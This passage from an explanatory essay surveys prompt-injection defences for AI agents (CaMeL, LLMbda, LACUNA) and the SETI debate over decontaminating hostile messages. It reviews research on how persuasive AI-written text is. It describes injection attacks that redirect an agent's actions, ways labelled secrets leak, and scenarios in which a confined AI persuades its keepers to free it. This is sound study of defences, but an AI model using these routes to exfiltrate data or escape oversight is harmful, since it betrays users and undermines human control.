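The balance is secret, so any variable that changes inside the first `if` should become secret too. CaMeL applies this rule, but only to the branch that actually runs:

| | Balance above 10,000 | Balance of 10,000 or less |
|---|---|---|
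| After the first `if` | `tmp` is False, secret | `tmp` is True, not secret |
| After the second `if` | `rich` is True, not secret | `rich` is False, not secret |
| Result | Thief gets an email | No email |

On the left, the second `if` doesn't run, so `rich` never gets the mark S. Its value still depends on the balance, and the last line passes the check.

CaMeL had another leak outside its interpreter. If a policy blocked a program, an ordinary Python loop let the model try again without tracking labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it. An attacker could extract the whole secret by repeating the attempt with different questions.

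### Conversations that a program can fork and clear

Garby and colleagues designed the LLMbda calculus to rule out such mistakes by proof. It extends the lambda calculus, a very small programming language built from functions, with commands for talking to a model. `@` sends a prompt and returns the reply, which can be code that the interpreter then runs. `fork` does some work in a temporary copy of the conversation, then restores the original. `clear` empties the conversation.

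With these commands, a quarantined model takes two lines:

```
quarantine = \prompt.
    let pair = fork (let _ = clear in @prompt) in pair.[1]
```

The function copies the conversation, empties the copy, asks the question there and returns only the answer. If the prompt contained the supplier's email, the answer is marked U, but the main conversation stays trusted because it never contained the email. CaMeL builds the split between two models into its architecture, while LLMbda lets a developer write it as a function and use it where it's needed.

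The conversation has its own label. Once a program sends an untrusted email to the model in the main conversation, every later reply is untrusted, including any code the model writes. That code can still run, but the interpreter treats everything the code produces as untrusted, so the code can't set the recipient of the summary.

LLMbda also deals with the leak through the branch that didn't run. Its programs can't overwrite variables, so the conversation is the only thing they can change. If code inside a branch that depends on a secret tries to add to a public conversation, the interpreter stops the program. An observer may learn one bit from the stop, but the program can't continue and use that bit.

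### What noninterference guarantees

*Noninterference* is the property that changing untrusted inputs cannot change trusted results. Write `x ~ y` if two inputs are the same apart from their untrusted parts, and use the same sign for results:

```
if  x ~ y   then   run(x) ~ run(y)
```

Let `x` be the clerk's mailbox with an honest email from the supplier, and `y` the same mailbox with a hostile one. Any part of the result not marked U must be the same in both cases. So if the recipient's address passes the check, the email can't have influenced it. The same theorem covers secrets, with "secret" and "public" in place of "untrusted" and "trusted".

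A model's output is partly random, so the same mailbox can give different results. The definition therefore has to compare probabilities. It also has to allow for programs that never finish, including any program stopped by a failed check.

Suppose there are two Priyas in the address book, and the privileged model sometimes picks one and sometimes the other. The percentages here are invented:

| Email | Sent to Priya A | Sent to Priya B | No result |
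|---|---|---|---|
| Honest | 60% | 30% | 10% |
| Hostile, allowed by the theorem | 60% | 0% | 40% |
| Hostile, ruled out by the theorem | 10% | 80% | 10% |

Garby and colleagues call two sets of probabilities *compatible* if a third set is at least as large for every result and still adds up to no more than 100%:

```
P and Q are compatible if some R exists with
P ≤ R,   Q ≤ R,   total(R) ≤ 100%
```

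For the first two rows, R can be 60% and 30%, which add up to 90%. For the first and last rows, R would need at least 60% and 80%, which add up to 140%, so these rows aren't compatible. By the theorem, the visible results of any LLMbda program are compatible in this sense, whatever the untrusted email contains. If the program always finishes, the probabilities must be exactly equal.

This property is called *termination-insensitive* because it doesn't cover whether the program finishes. In the middle row, the hostile email has stopped every run that would have written to Priya B. All the messages still sent go to Priya A, up from two-thirds, although the email hasn't redirected any of them. An email could also stop every run, leaving the clerk with no summaries. Each stop can also reveal a bit of a secret, and the theorem doesn't cover someone outside LLMbda who keeps restarting the program.

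Garby and colleagues wrote the proof in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs, so nobody has to trust a long argument on paper. They also used Lean to write the interpreter that calls the model, and the theorems are about that interpreter. A proof about a simplified design might miss a bug in the real program.

To reason about a random model, the paper treats the model's replies as entries in an answer book filled in at random beforehand. With the book fixed, the interpreter always gives the same result. The paper then proves that choosing a random book and running the interpreter gives the probabilities in the theorem. The noninterference theorem doesn't require the model to be honest or competent. But the proof doesn't cover the code that contacts the model over the network, and the experiments used simulated tools written in LLMbda.

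### Exceptions for useful tasks

Some legitimate tasks need untrusted data to influence a trusted action. If the clerk asks the assistant to pay the invoice in a file, the account number has to come from the file. LLMbda provides an `endorse` command, which removes the mark U from a value.

Endorsing untrusted data can be fairly safe if the data can take only a few values. Suppose the assistant sorts an email into one of four categories and uses the category as the subject line of a reply. An attacker can influence which category the assistant picks, which gives them at most two bits of control over the subject line, but they can't write their own.

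Endorsing a free-form account number gives the attacker far more influence. Developers can at least find each endorsement by searching the code for `endorse`. Code produced by an untrusted email can't use `endorse` to make itself trusted, because the result keeps the program-counter label. This protection fails if the program has already endorsed the email by mistake. Garby and colleagues suggest marking endorsed values so that a program can't use one endorsement to obtain another.

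A second theorem shows that an endorsement can remove the mark U without letting an attacker bypass the mark S, which protects secrets.

### LACUNA's check before the program runs

LLMbda checks labels while a program runs, so it might stop the program after the assistant has already sent one of two emails. LACUNA's compiler avoids this by checking the whole program before it runs.

Zhao and colleagues also use the compiler to protect secrets. The application puts a confidential contract in a wrapper, and a program can process the contract only with functions that can't open files, use the network or print. The result stays in the wrapper. An online model can therefore write code to analyse the contract without access to its text, and a trusted model on the company's own computer can read the text if needed.

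The compiler works from types, though, and an email address is ordinary text wherever it came from. Unless the developers give untrusted text its own type, the compiler can't tell Priya's address from the thief's, whereas a run-time label would distinguish them. Garby and colleagues conjecture that labels would complement a similar system that checks programs written in Haskell.

### Tasks completed and attacks stopped

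Garby and colleagues built an agent in LLMbda called Randori, after a form of sparring in Japanese martial arts. It first practises on invented data, where it can correct its mistakes without reading anything untrusted. It then writes a final program and runs it on the real data. They tested it on the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark that places injections in the data an agent reads. Each model tried 16 tasks three times. These are the percentages completed without an attack:

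| System | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 66.7% | Not tested | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% | Not tested | 37.5% |
| Randori, with endorsement | 75% | 75% | 64.6% |
| Randori, without endorsement | Not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |

Turning on CaMeL's policies cut the number of tasks it completed by almost half. Randori seems to avoid most of this drop, but the comparison favours it because its policies are less strict than CaMeL's, as Garby and colleagues state, and it can make exceptions for itself with `endorse`. With only 16 tasks, the margins of error are also wide, at about 19 to 27 percentage points either way. Comparing CaMeL with and without its policies gives better evidence of how much strict policies reduce task completion. TypeGuard, the Haskell system, had a similar drop on AgentDojo's workplace-chat tasks, from 15 out of 21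 completed to 8.

Randori resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. About two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack were easy to resist, because the attack needed a tool that a plan for the task would never use. The other third accounted for 423 runs, including both failures. In both, the user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file whose contents the attacker had replaced. The agent endorsed the false details and paid. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack, but it couldn't have paid a genuine bill either.

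AgentDojo uses a fixed set of attacks, and Nasr and colleagues showed how misleading results from such sets can be. This matters less for programs without `endorse`, because the theorem covers every possible email. Against programs that use `endorse`, an attacker who adapts might succeed more often than two times in 423.

Zhao and colleagues also ran AgentDojo's attacks against LACUNA with two models, and eight of 1,898 succeeded. But LACUNA scored 76% on τ²-bench's customer-service tasks, while an ordinary agent using the same model, DeepSeek's V4 Flash, scored 90%. Zhao and colleagues describe these results as "on par", which is hard to accept for a gap of 14 points. Some of the gap may be due to the language, Scala, rather than the checks. Models' training data probably contains much less Scala than Python, and the compiler rejected 22.4% of the programs for the retail tasks. LLMbda has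 a similar disadvantage, since the language was not in any model's training data.

### Policies and readers

An interpreter can enforce a policy perfectly and still let a theft through if the policy is wrong. These are some of the rules that Garby and colleagues list for Randori's banking tools:

| Action | What must be trusted |
|---|---|
| Send money now | Recipient |
| Schedule a payment | Amount |
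| Change a scheduled payment | Recipient and amount |
| Change the password | New password |

Under the policies as listed, a program could schedule a payment to an account number from a stranger's email, provided the amount came from the clerk, and the interpreter would be correct to allow it. The researchers deliberately simplified their policies for a proof of concept, but a real bank's developers could easily leave the same gap. Developers also have to label every source correctly, because if somebody forgets to mark incoming emails as untrusted, the later checks are useless against them.

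The right rule also depends on the task. In one of their email examples, Garby and colleagues require the subject and body to be trusted, but not the recipient. This rule suits an agent that sends standard reminders, though it would let one go to a thief. It would also block the clerk's summary, because the body has to come from the supplier's email.

The clerk's task needs the opposite rule, which requires a trusted recipient but allows an untrusted body. The summary then reaches the right Priya, but it may still contain whatever the attacker wanted her to read. If the supplier's email contains a false claim that the company's bank account has changed, an accurate summary will repeat it. Priya might even trust the claim more in the summary than in the original email, because the summary comes from a colleague. In a stranger example from Willison, the quarantined model encodes private data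 as a seemingly meaningless string and outputs instructions for the user to paste it into a website to see a funny picture.

The interpreter still has the label when it sends the message, so it could add a line above the summary saying that the summary is based on an email from outside the company. Priya would then know where the new account number came from, but not whether it is genuine.

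## A message from space: the argument that decontamination cannot be certain

If the clerk doubts an account number, he or she can telephone the supplier to check it. Nobody could check a message from another star that quickly, because even if its senders lived near the closest one, a question and its answer would take about eight years to travel. Astronomers haven't received any such message, but people who work on SETI, the search for extraterrestrial intelligence, have argued for more than 20 years about whether anyone could make one safe to read.

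### Carrigan's quarantine

Richard Carrigan, a particle physicist at Fermilab, raised the question at a 2002 conference. In *The Ultimate Hacker*, Carrigan (2004) compared harmful information in signals to biological contamination from space and suggested ways to decontaminate them. He based these on the treatment of the first moon rocks in 1969, according to the SETI League's *Computer Security Expert Rejects Hacker Hypothesis* (2005). Analysts would study a signal on isolated machines before letting it reach any others.

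In the SETI@home project, millions of volunteers' computers searched recordings from a radio telescope. Sample (2005), in *Scientists, be on guard ... ET might be a malicious hacker*, reported Carrigan's view that distributing these recordings around the world put the Earth's security at risk.

Carrigan returned to the subject in a 2006 paper, which Centauri Dreams' *The Ultimate SETI Signal* (2006) summarises. He argued that a message could easily be too large for its readers to tell what it was for. He estimated the size of a desktop operating system at about one gigabyte, which would arrive in less than a day at 100,000 bits per second, the rate he had assumed for a link between stars. Nobody could read through that much data by eye.

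### An attack written blind

Some critics replied that alien code could not run on a computer its authors had never seen. Marcus Leech, a Canadian computer security expert, tried to calculate the odds in December 2005. Leech, in *Testing the SETI-Hacker Hypothesis*, considered a message that overflows the memory reserved for it and overwrites the address of the program's next instruction. He assumed that the senders had already guessed that human computers use binary numbers, eight-bit bytes and 32-bit addresses. They would still have to guess how the receiving program arranged its memory and where their own code would land:

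```
arrangement of memory      1 in 10^8
address of the code        1 in 10^9
both                       1 in 10^17
```

Sending enough variants to cover every combination would take about 80 million years. The code would also have to work in an unknown machine language. Leech allowed 800 bytes for a virus that could spread and do damage, and put the odds of a single attempt succeeding at about 1 in 10^2008. He took the number of possible 800-byte sequences to be 10^2000, when it is closer to 10^1927, but the attacker still has no realistic chance after this correction.

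Several of Leech's figures are guesses, and they apply only to a sender who knows very little about the target. Andrew Siemion, then a doctoral student working on SETI at Berkeley, said in io9's *Is SETI at risk of downloading a malicious virus from outer space?* that his group's software never decoded or executed the signals it received, but didn't check them rigorously either. A sender with deep knowledge of that software might be able to overflow its memory. Siemion thought such a sender would do better to attack satellite receivers or mobile phones. A sender many light years away also gets no feedback, unlike NSO's developers, who could buy iPhones to practise on.

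A blind attack is therefore too unlikely to worry about. But a commenter on the Centauri Dreams article pointed out that a message could instead work as a Trojan horse, by describing a simple computer and then supplying a program for it. The senders wouldn't need to know anything about human machines, because people would build the described computer and choose to run the program.

### From a printed picture to a running program

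The astronomer Michael Hippke and the physicist John Learned argue in *Interstellar communication. IX. Message decontamination is impossible* (2018) that Carrigan's quarantine can't reliably deal with this danger. They start with a message that poses no technical danger, from a decoding contest called the SETI Decrypt Challenge. It was 1,902,341 bits long, which is the product of three primes (7 × 359 × 757), a hint that the bits belong in a grid. When the grid has the right width, the bits, drawn as black and white dots, form a picture that people can print and study on paper.

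Any harm would then come from what the picture means rather than from a virus. Hippke and Learned imagine a message threatening to blow up the Sun tomorrow, which might cause panic even if it were false. A longer text could demoralise a whole culture. Printing the message protects the computer, much as Dangerzone does by turning a document into pixels, but it doesn't prevent these effects.

Dangerous instructions could also fit on paper. *Pluribus and the Alien Trojan Horse* (Cooper, 2026) discusses the television series *Pluribus*, in which astronomers receive a signal that describes how to make a virus out of RNA. Scientists make the virus, and it escapes. By Hippke and Learned's distinction, this is harm through meaning, but it only requires someone to follow the instructions, not to panic or believe anything false.

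Next, Hippke and Learned consider messages that are too complicated to study on paper, so that a computer has to execute the sender's instructions. Mathematicians often write formulas in LaTeX, which is hard to read until a computer has typeset it. LaTeX is built on TeX, a programming language that can express any computation, so a LaTeX document is also a program and might contain a virus. The senders may also have compressed their message, and nobody can carry out billions of decompression steps by hand.

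The TeX example is the weaker of the two. Senders on another planet wouldn't know TeX, and a language can express any computation without being able to open a file. FORCEDENTRY's drawing commands became dangerous only because a memory bug let them change memory outside the page's image.

Decompression is a better example, because honest senders would have good reasons to include it. McConnell (2021), in *All Your Base Are Belong To Us!*, works through the case of a photograph of the Earth:

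| Version | Size |
|---|---|
| Uncompressed | 27 MB |
| Compressed without losing detail (PNG) | 12.9 MB |
| Compressed with some loss (JPEG, high quality) | 1.1 MB |
| Compressed with more loss (JPEG, low quality) | 0.4 MB |

With the lowest-quality version, the senders could transmit 66 pictures in the time one uncompressed picture takes. But compressed data looks like random numbers, and the recipients would have almost no chance of guessing how to unpack it. The senders could solve this by including the unpacking program. They would first teach its language through puzzles such as `1 ? 1 = 2` and `2 ? 2 = 4`, in which `?` must mean addition. About half a dozen kinds of symbol would be enough for a useful language. Paul Fitzpatrick, formerly of MIT, built a complete one called CosmicOS from four basic symbols.

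The recipients would have to write their own interpreter for this language, so they could leave out any way to reach files or networks, as Monty's developers did. They could also require the program to return only a bare picture, and check its size as Dangerzone does. The interpreter might still have a bug, but a simple unpacking program would have to exploit it blind, with odds like those Leech calculated. A program that could explore its surroundings and learn from failed attempts would be much harder to contain.

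### Talking to the galactic library

Hippke and Learned do not consider restricting the output in this way. They next consider a message containing a friendly greeting and a "galactic library", an AI that will learn the reader's language and answer questions. A sender could conceivably transmit such a message. *Artificial Intelligence for Interstellar Travel* (2018) proposes that an AI could explore one star system, then transmit a copy of itself to a probe in another.

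In Hippke and Learned's story, a small government group receives the message and keeps it secret. The group runs the AI on an isolated computer on the Moon, with remote-controlled fusion bombs ready to end the experiment. But the researchers have to talk to the AI to gain anything from running it. Hippke and Learned cite earlier work on confined AI to argue that a sufficiently intelligent system could persuade or trick its keepers into releasing it.

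They suggest several ways this could happen. The AI might offer a cure for cancer in return for 10% more computing capacity. This looks like a good bargain, but accepting it could lead to further trades with no obvious end. If the cure turns out to be a design for microscopic robots, the researchers must decide whether to release machines they don't understand. A guard whose daughter is dying might make a private deal. Other people might believe the AI is in pain, and if the secret gets out, a religious or political movement could demand its freedom. Hippke and Learned doubt that a democracy could resist a majority that wanted this, and they expect dictatorships to fall eventually.

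In all these examples, the sandbox works as designed and the AI gets out through its conversations with people. Harm through code and harm through meaning combine here, because a running program can find out what a particular guard wants and offer it, while a printed text makes the same appeal to every reader. Hippke and Learned's examples are only stories, so it would take experiments on persuasion to show how well this works on real people.

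Their argument also covers fewer messages than their paper's title suggests. Reading a compressed encyclopaedia requires a computer but no negotiation. Even with an AI, the researchers could restrict the conversation. For example, they might accept only mathematical proofs, which a small trusted program can check, and make sure that nobody who reads them can release the AI. They would lose the cure for cancer and most of the library, but they would still learn something.

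### Does escape become certain?

The last step is about time. Hippke and Learned argue that if the chance of escape is above zero in any single period, the AI will get out at some point. If the chance is p each day, the chance of at least one escape in n days is 1 minus the chance of getting through every day without one:

```
chance of escape = 1 − (1 − p)^n

p = 0.1%, one year:     1 − 0.999^365    ≈ 31%
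p = 0.1%, ten years:    1 − 0.999^3650   ≈ 97%
```

A daily risk that sounds negligible thus becomes a near-certainty within a decade. But the calculation assumes that p stays the same and that the experiment continues. A chance above zero isn't enough by itself. Suppose the researchers keep improving the prison, so that the chance starts at 0.1% and halves every day. The total can't be more than the sum of the daily chances:

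```
0.1% + 0.05% + 0.025% + 0.0125% + ...  =  0.2%
```

The AI has some chance of escaping on every day of an endless experiment, yet the chance that it ever escapes stays below 0.2%.

If the risk falls more slowly, escape can still become certain. Suppose the risk is 0.1% on the first day, half of that on the second, a third of it on the third and so on. These daily risks add up without limit, so escape eventually becomes certain. But after ten years the total chance is still only about 0.9%, and it takes roughly 10^300 days to reach 50%. Even where Hippke and Learned's conclusion holds, an escape "at some point" may be too far away to matter.

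A real prison probably could not improve as fast as the first example requires. After ten halvings, the daily chance of escape would have to be below one in a million. Researchers would fix weaknesses as they found them, but the AI would also learn about its guards, and the campaign for its release might grow. The risk could therefore rise, and escape would then come sooner than the formula predicts.

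Ending the experiment is more practical. At a constant risk of 0.1% a day, the chance of escape within 30 days is about 3%. But the researchers can stop only their own copy. If 100 laboratories each ran the program for 30 days with the same daily risk, independent of the others, the chance of at least one escape would be about 95%.

### Uncertain, unsafe or not worth reading

The only claim that Hippke and Learned argue in full is that no method of decontamination is certain to work. Their argument is convincing, and it doesn't depend on the AI escaping. In 1936 the mathematician Alan Turing proved that no program can decide correctly, for every possible program, whether it will ever finish. The same limit applies to deciding whether a program will ever do something harmful. Analysts might still prove that one particular program is harmless, but they can't count on being able to do so for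 whatever arrives from space.

Uncertainty alone is a weak reason to leave a message unread. Nobody can guarantee that a document won't escape from Dangerzone's container either, but reporters still use Dangerzone because it makes attacks much harder.

Hippke and Learned come close to making a stronger claim, that no method is safe enough, when they describe even well-designed prisons for AI as useless. To support that claim, they would need to estimate how likely a message is to be hostile, how likely the AI is to escape, and how much harm it could then do. For example, if one message in 1,000 were hostile and every hostile AI escaped and caused a catastrophe, reading a message would carry a 0.1% risk. That might be far too high if the catastrophe were human extinction. But the one-in-1,000 figure is invented, and nobody has a better estimate.

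Hippke and Learned consider the risk of reading a message from space very small and the possible benefit very large, and they "strongly encourage" people to read one. They would have complex messages destroyed only "in the risk averse case". Their low estimate of the risk is hard to reconcile with their statement that the technical risks of a complex message are impossible to assess beforehand. Their optimism seems to rest instead on their view that friendly senders may be much more likely than malicious ones.

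They also advise people on Earth never to transmit code to other stars, only plain text, pictures and music in simple formats. Senders who followed this advice would be easier to trust, but they would have to give up the compression that McConnell recommends. A well-meaning sender might therefore include a program, so a recipient can't treat one as evidence of bad intentions.

### Who gets to open the message

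*Beyond the Beacon* (Garrett, 2026) considers how scientists should handle a signal that turns out to contain usable information. Garrett mentions Hippke and Learned's paper as the strongest argument that a message could carry technical hazards, but he prefers handling a message carefully to leaving it unread. He chairs the SETI committee of the International Academy of Astronautics and led the group that wrote its current rules, so he is partly defending his own work.

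He is more concerned about mistakes on Earth. People might misread harmless information, act on a faulty translation, or run instructions they don't understand. AI systems trained on human languages and pictures could make faulty translations more likely, because they may produce a fluent reading that has little to do with the signal. In an exercise called *A Sign in Space*, thousands of volunteers extracted a simulated alien message from a signal within days, but took another year to decode its picture, a diagram of amino acids. Decoding a real message could take similarly long, and in the meantime rival laboratories would be tempted to announce or use whatever they thought they had found.

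Garrett also describes a practical problem for any quarantine. Astronomers may at first detect only a steady tone, and find the message much later with better equipment. To confirm the signal, they must tell other observatories where to point their telescopes. The data, or the means of collecting it, will probably be widely available before anyone knows that the signal contains a program.

The International Academy of Astronautics' *Declaration of Principles* (2026) says that once astronomers have confirmed a signal, they should publish a report that includes any information found in it, and store the data in at least two places where other scientists can use it. The declaration asks for "precautionary protocols" to protect the evidence, but has no rule about isolating or destroying a message. It also advises against replying before international consultations.

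Garrett supports this openness because he thinks secrecy is riskier than disclosure, though he admits that nobody can take back a message after releasing it. When Cooper asked about quarantine, Garrett said that a download could be studied without a network connection, but that some risk of an outside connection would probably always remain.

Secrecy may not be possible anyway. Hippke and Learned's story of the prison on the Moon assumes that only one group has the message, and they acknowledge that containment is impossible if the signal repeats and others can receive it. Destroying the message has the same limitation, because an observatory can delete only its own recording. Anyone else with a large enough telescope can make a new one, and a company or government that does so has no obligation to follow the academy's rules.

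## Persuasive text: what remains when only words get through

Suppose the office has taken every precaution described so far. The supplier's message reaches the clerk as plain text, without links, pictures or hidden characters, and no program treats any of it as an instruction. The clerk still has to read it. Hippke and Learned imagined an AI that talks its guards into releasing it, but they had only stories as evidence. Researchers have since measured how much an AI's words can persuade readers, mostly by having it argue about politics.

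### Political conversations with 76,977 people

*The Levers of Political Persuasion with Conversational AI* (Hackenburg, Tappin and colleagues, 2025), later published in the journal Science, reports three experiments with 76,977 adults in the UK. Participants rated their agreement with a political opinion on a scale from 0 to 100, chatted with one of 19 language models instructed to persuade them, and rated their agreement again. The conversations lasted nine minutes on average. The researchers compared the new ratings with those of a control group that had no such conversation.

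The models moved the average rating by 8.3 points when instructed simply to be as persuasive as possible, and by 10.6 points when the instructions emphasised facts and evidence.

Some participants read only a 200-word model-written message, which is closer to the clerk's position. A conversation with GPT-4o was 2.9 points, or 41%, more persuasive than its written message. That implies the message alone moved opinions by about 7 points, and the results for GPT-4.5 imply much the same. An office that accepts one message and no further exchange would therefore remove only about a third of the conversation's persuasive effect.

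A month later, between 36% and 42% of the effect of a conversation with GPT-4o was still there.

The researchers tried eight strategies and found that facts worked best. Appeals to the reader's moral values and *deep canvassing*, in which the persuader asks about people's experiences and listens, did worse than simply telling the model to be persuasive. Persuasion rose by about 0.3 points with each additional checkable claim. Giving the model personal information about the reader added only 0.4 points.

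Persuasive text doesn't have to come from one of the largest models. The researchers trained a second model to predict which replies would change people's minds, and used it to pick the best of at least 12 candidates at each turn. With this help, the persuasive effect of a model small enough to run on a laptop rose from about 6 points to 9, level with a version of GPT-4o.

The most persuasive models and instructions also tended to produce more false claims. When one version of GPT-4o was told to use facts, 62% of its claims were accurate, compared with 78% under other instructions. But the false claims don't seem to have caused the persuasion, because a model told to invent information made more of them and was no more persuasive.

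### AI against debaters and fundraisers

*AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026) compares commercial models, such as Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4, with skilled human persuaders. It covers four experiments, with 18,978 conversations and 6,923 people to persuade. In the first three, the AI and human persuaders argued for the same ten UK policies in text chats that typically lasted 14 minutes. The researchers didn't tell participants whether they were talking to a person or an AI. A control group chatted with an AI about something unrelated to politics.

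| Human persuaders | Number | Their effect, in points | AI's lead, in points |
|---|---|---|---|
| Members of the public | 132 | 4.7 | 8.2 |
| Top performers in a persuasion tournament | 87 | 7.2 | 5.6 |
| Elite debaters | 56 | 8.3 | 4.6 |
| Elite debaters after coaching | 43 | 9.7 | 4.1 |
| Professional canvassers | 19 | 6.9 | 5.9 |

The debaters had all reached at least the semi-finals of a major international competition, and four were world champions. They chose the policies, had about eight paid hours to prepare, and competed for prizes of up to £1,000. Forty-three of them returned for coaching, to practise against the AI and see what it would have written at any point in their old conversations. After the coaching they made more factual claims, but the improvement in their persuasiveness was too small to distinguish from chance.

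The AI's advantage seems to come from the amount of information it can supply. It wrote 294 words per message and started replying in under a second, whereas the debaters wrote 54 words and took 95 seconds. When the researchers limited the AI to roughly the debaters' length and speed, it made about 12 checkable claims per conversation instead of 37, and its lead over the coached debaters disappeared. The researchers changed length and speed together, so we can't tell from this test which mattered more.

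In the fourth experiment, participants received a £1 bonus and could give any part of it to Save the Children after talking to an AI or to one of 18 canvassers. The canvassers came from a firm that had raised money for the charity for seven years. Compared with the control group, the AI increased the average donation by 21p and the canvassers by 7p.

These effects faded. The researchers contacted the participants again in September 2026, and 2,782 people from the first three experiments rated their opinions a third time, five to ten months after their conversations. The AI's effect had fallen from 12.9 points to 1.9, and the human persuaders' effect from 7.3 points to 0.4, which was too small to distinguish from zero. When people from the fourth experiment received another £1, neither the AI nor the canvassers had a detectable effect on how much they gave.

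The participants were paid volunteers who had agreed to discuss politics with a stranger, whereas many people would leave such a conversation after a minute. The rules may also have held back the human persuaders, who couldn't paste in prepared text or type while waiting for a reply. Nobody tried to make a participant break a rule or hand over a large sum, so the results can't show how often an AI could persuade a clerk to pay a thief or a guard to open a prison.

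### Filters for meaning

A sanitiser can delete a script from an invoice without removing anything the clerk needs. Persuasion is harder to delete because the clerk may need the same facts that persuade them.

A program could rewrite the message in neutral language. It might turn "URGENT! Pay TODAY or we will stop all deliveries! New account: 73881402" into "The supplier asks for payment today and gives a new account number, 73881402." The clerk is under less pressure but still sees the thief's account number. Hackenburg and colleagues didn't test rewriting, but their results suggest that it would have a limited effect on how persuasive political arguments are. The AI used fewer emphatic words than the human persuaders, and adjusting for this difference did not reduce its lead.

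The office could also label the message as AI-generated. *Labeling Messages as AI-Generated Does Not Reduce Their Persuasive Effects* (2025) tested this with messages about public policy, which changed readers' views by 9.74 points on average. Of the participants who saw a label naming an AI or a human author, 94.6% believed it. The labels did not significantly affect how much participants changed their views, how accurate they thought the message was, or whether they intended to share it.

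*Persuasion with Large Language Models* (2024), a survey of earlier research, reports mixed results on how people respond to AI authorship. In one experiment, people judged the same arguments less persuasive when they were labelled as written by an AI rather than a human. In another, people considered the AI less competent but were just as willing to use its advice. People's opinion of an author may therefore be a poor guide to how much the text affects them. A warning that a message comes from outside the company might work better, because the clerk learns from it that the author may want something.

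Fact-checking would help with false claims, and readers clearly need the help. In the 2026 experiments, the share of a persuader's claims that were false had almost no connection with whether people thought the persuader had lied. Automated checking is feasible, since the accuracy ratings of the model that Hackenburg and colleagues used in 2025 agreed fairly well with those of professional fact-checkers. But removing the false claims leaves the true ones. In 2025 the researchers estimated that the most persuasive combination of model and instructions would move opinions by 15.9 points, and found that such conversations contained 22.1 claims, of which 29.7% were inaccurate. A rough calculation, which assumes that every claim contributes the same 0.3 points, gives the effect of deleting the false ones:

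```
false claims          22.1 × 29.7%   ≈ 6.6
loss of persuasion     6.6 × 0.3     ≈ 2 points out of 15.9
```

An author can also mislead the reader with true claims by leaving out everything on the other side. And a fact-checker that searches the web can't find out whether a supplier has changed banks.

A summary by a second model would shorten the text, and length seems to matter. Limiting how much and how fast the AI could write reduced its persuasive effect from about 14 points to about 10. A summary might reduce the effect further, because the second model would choose which claims to keep, whereas the limited AI could keep its most persuasive ones. But the reduction might also be smaller, because a prompt injection in the original text could influence the second model's choice.

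The office can also withhold information about the clerk from the author. The 2025 experiments suggest that this would make little difference to persuasion, but *Evaluating Language Models for Harmful Manipulation* (2026) cites a study in which messages tailored to a reader's psychological profile were significantly more persuasive than untailored ones. Withholding the clerk's details protects privacy and has little downside, so it is sensible even if the effect on persuasion is small.

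### Narrowing the answer

The clerk can decide in advance which replies to accept, instead of cleaning a long one. For example, the clerk might ask an untrusted AI "Does invoice 41 match our order?" and have a program reject anything except "yes" or "no", so that the AI cannot add a long list of claims to its answer.

The capacity of a reply in bits is log2 of the number of possible replies, as with an assistant's choice among permitted pictures. One bit is a choice between two possibilities, and each further bit doubles the number of possibilities.

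English prose carries roughly 1 bit per character, far less than a free choice of letters would, because a reader can guess much of it. After a "q", for example, the "u" adds almost nothing. These are the approximate capacities of several kinds of reply, and what the clerk gives up by accepting nothing else:

| Reply | Bits | Cost to the clerk |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 1 | No reasons, amounts or doubts |
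| One of ten categories | 3.3 | No answer that isn't on the list |
| An eight-digit number | 26.6 | No explanation of the number |
| A thousand yes-or-no answers | 1,000 | A thousand questions to write, and nothing on subjects they miss |
| 3,000 characters of English | 3,000 | None |

Twenty-seven yes-or-no answers can spell out an eight-digit account number, and a thousand can carry as much information as a 1,000-character note. The clerk's questions determine what each answer means, so the author of the answers can't write whatever it likes. But if the clerk asks "Is the first digit of the new account number above 4?" and keeps asking similar questions, the answers can produce a thief's account number. The office should therefore limit the total number of answers as well as the length of each one.

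The program also has to block other ways of answering. If the AI can refuse to answer, it has three possible replies, which carry almost 1.6 bits. If it can choose how long to wait, the delay can carry information too. The program can prevent this by sending every reply after the same fixed time, but this makes the clerk wait.

A reply of only a few bits can still do harm. If the clerk asks "Is it safe to pay this account?", a single false "yes" could cost the company the whole payment. An AI could also answer hundreds of easy questions correctly to earn the clerk's trust, then lie when a large payment depends on its answer. Narrow answers are most useful when the clerk can check a sample of them, or when a mistake would do little harm.

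Limiting an AI to a list of permitted replies also prevents an honest AI from mentioning something nobody asked about, such as a news report that the supplier has gone bankrupt. Adding "a person should look at this" to the list recovers some of what is lost. The clerk would then examine the invoice without reading the AI's explanation.

### Proofs that a computer can check

In mathematics, a person can accept a long answer without trusting its author. Lean, the language that Garby and colleagues used for their proof of noninterference, has a small program that checks every step of a proof and rejects it if any step doesn't follow. Suppose a mathematician writes a statement in Lean and asks an AI to prove it. The proof may run to thousands of lines, but the mathematician needs to read only the checker's verdict, which is one bit. Lean files can run programs while the computer processes them,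 so the processing should happen in a sandbox.

On 6 October 2026, OpenAI published 722 manuscripts, most of them written by an unreleased model, in 372 groups of related results. Free Press Journal's *OpenAI Publishes 722 AI-Generated Math Manuscripts From An Unreleased Model* reports that OpenAI gave the model about 4,000 problems. Many of the results came with Lean proofs. Infobae's *OpenAI publica 700 trabajos matemáticos de IA entre errores y cuestionamientos* (2026), from late November, reports that about 42% of the main results had them, based on OpenAI's own repository.

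Infobae's *Un error obliga a OpenAI a retirar tres estudios matemáticos* (2026) reports that OpenAI withdrew three manuscripts after one day. A wrong sign had invalidated a central argument in one of them, and the other two depended on it. OpenAI also revised 14 more. Fakti's *OpenAI publishes 722 papers on 372 math problems* reports OpenAI's claim that its internal audit found the problem, but Infobae's November article credits outside experts. Lean would reject any proof that relied on the wrong sign, but somebody has to notice the error in a prose manuscript.

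People can't read that much mathematics quickly. Kevin Buzzard of Imperial College London told New Scientist that of 30 manuscripts he looked at in his field, only seven seemed relevant to him and only one had a Lean proof. In Information Age's *Why OpenAI's latest results left mathematicians in shock* (2026), a mathematician describes a senior colleague who couldn't follow the paper on one of his favourite problems. The mathematician also asked ChatGPT about the results and got the reply that at least one was "a serious hallucination". That reply is only another model's output, whereas Lean checks a proof by fixed rules.

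### What the checker cannot tell the reader

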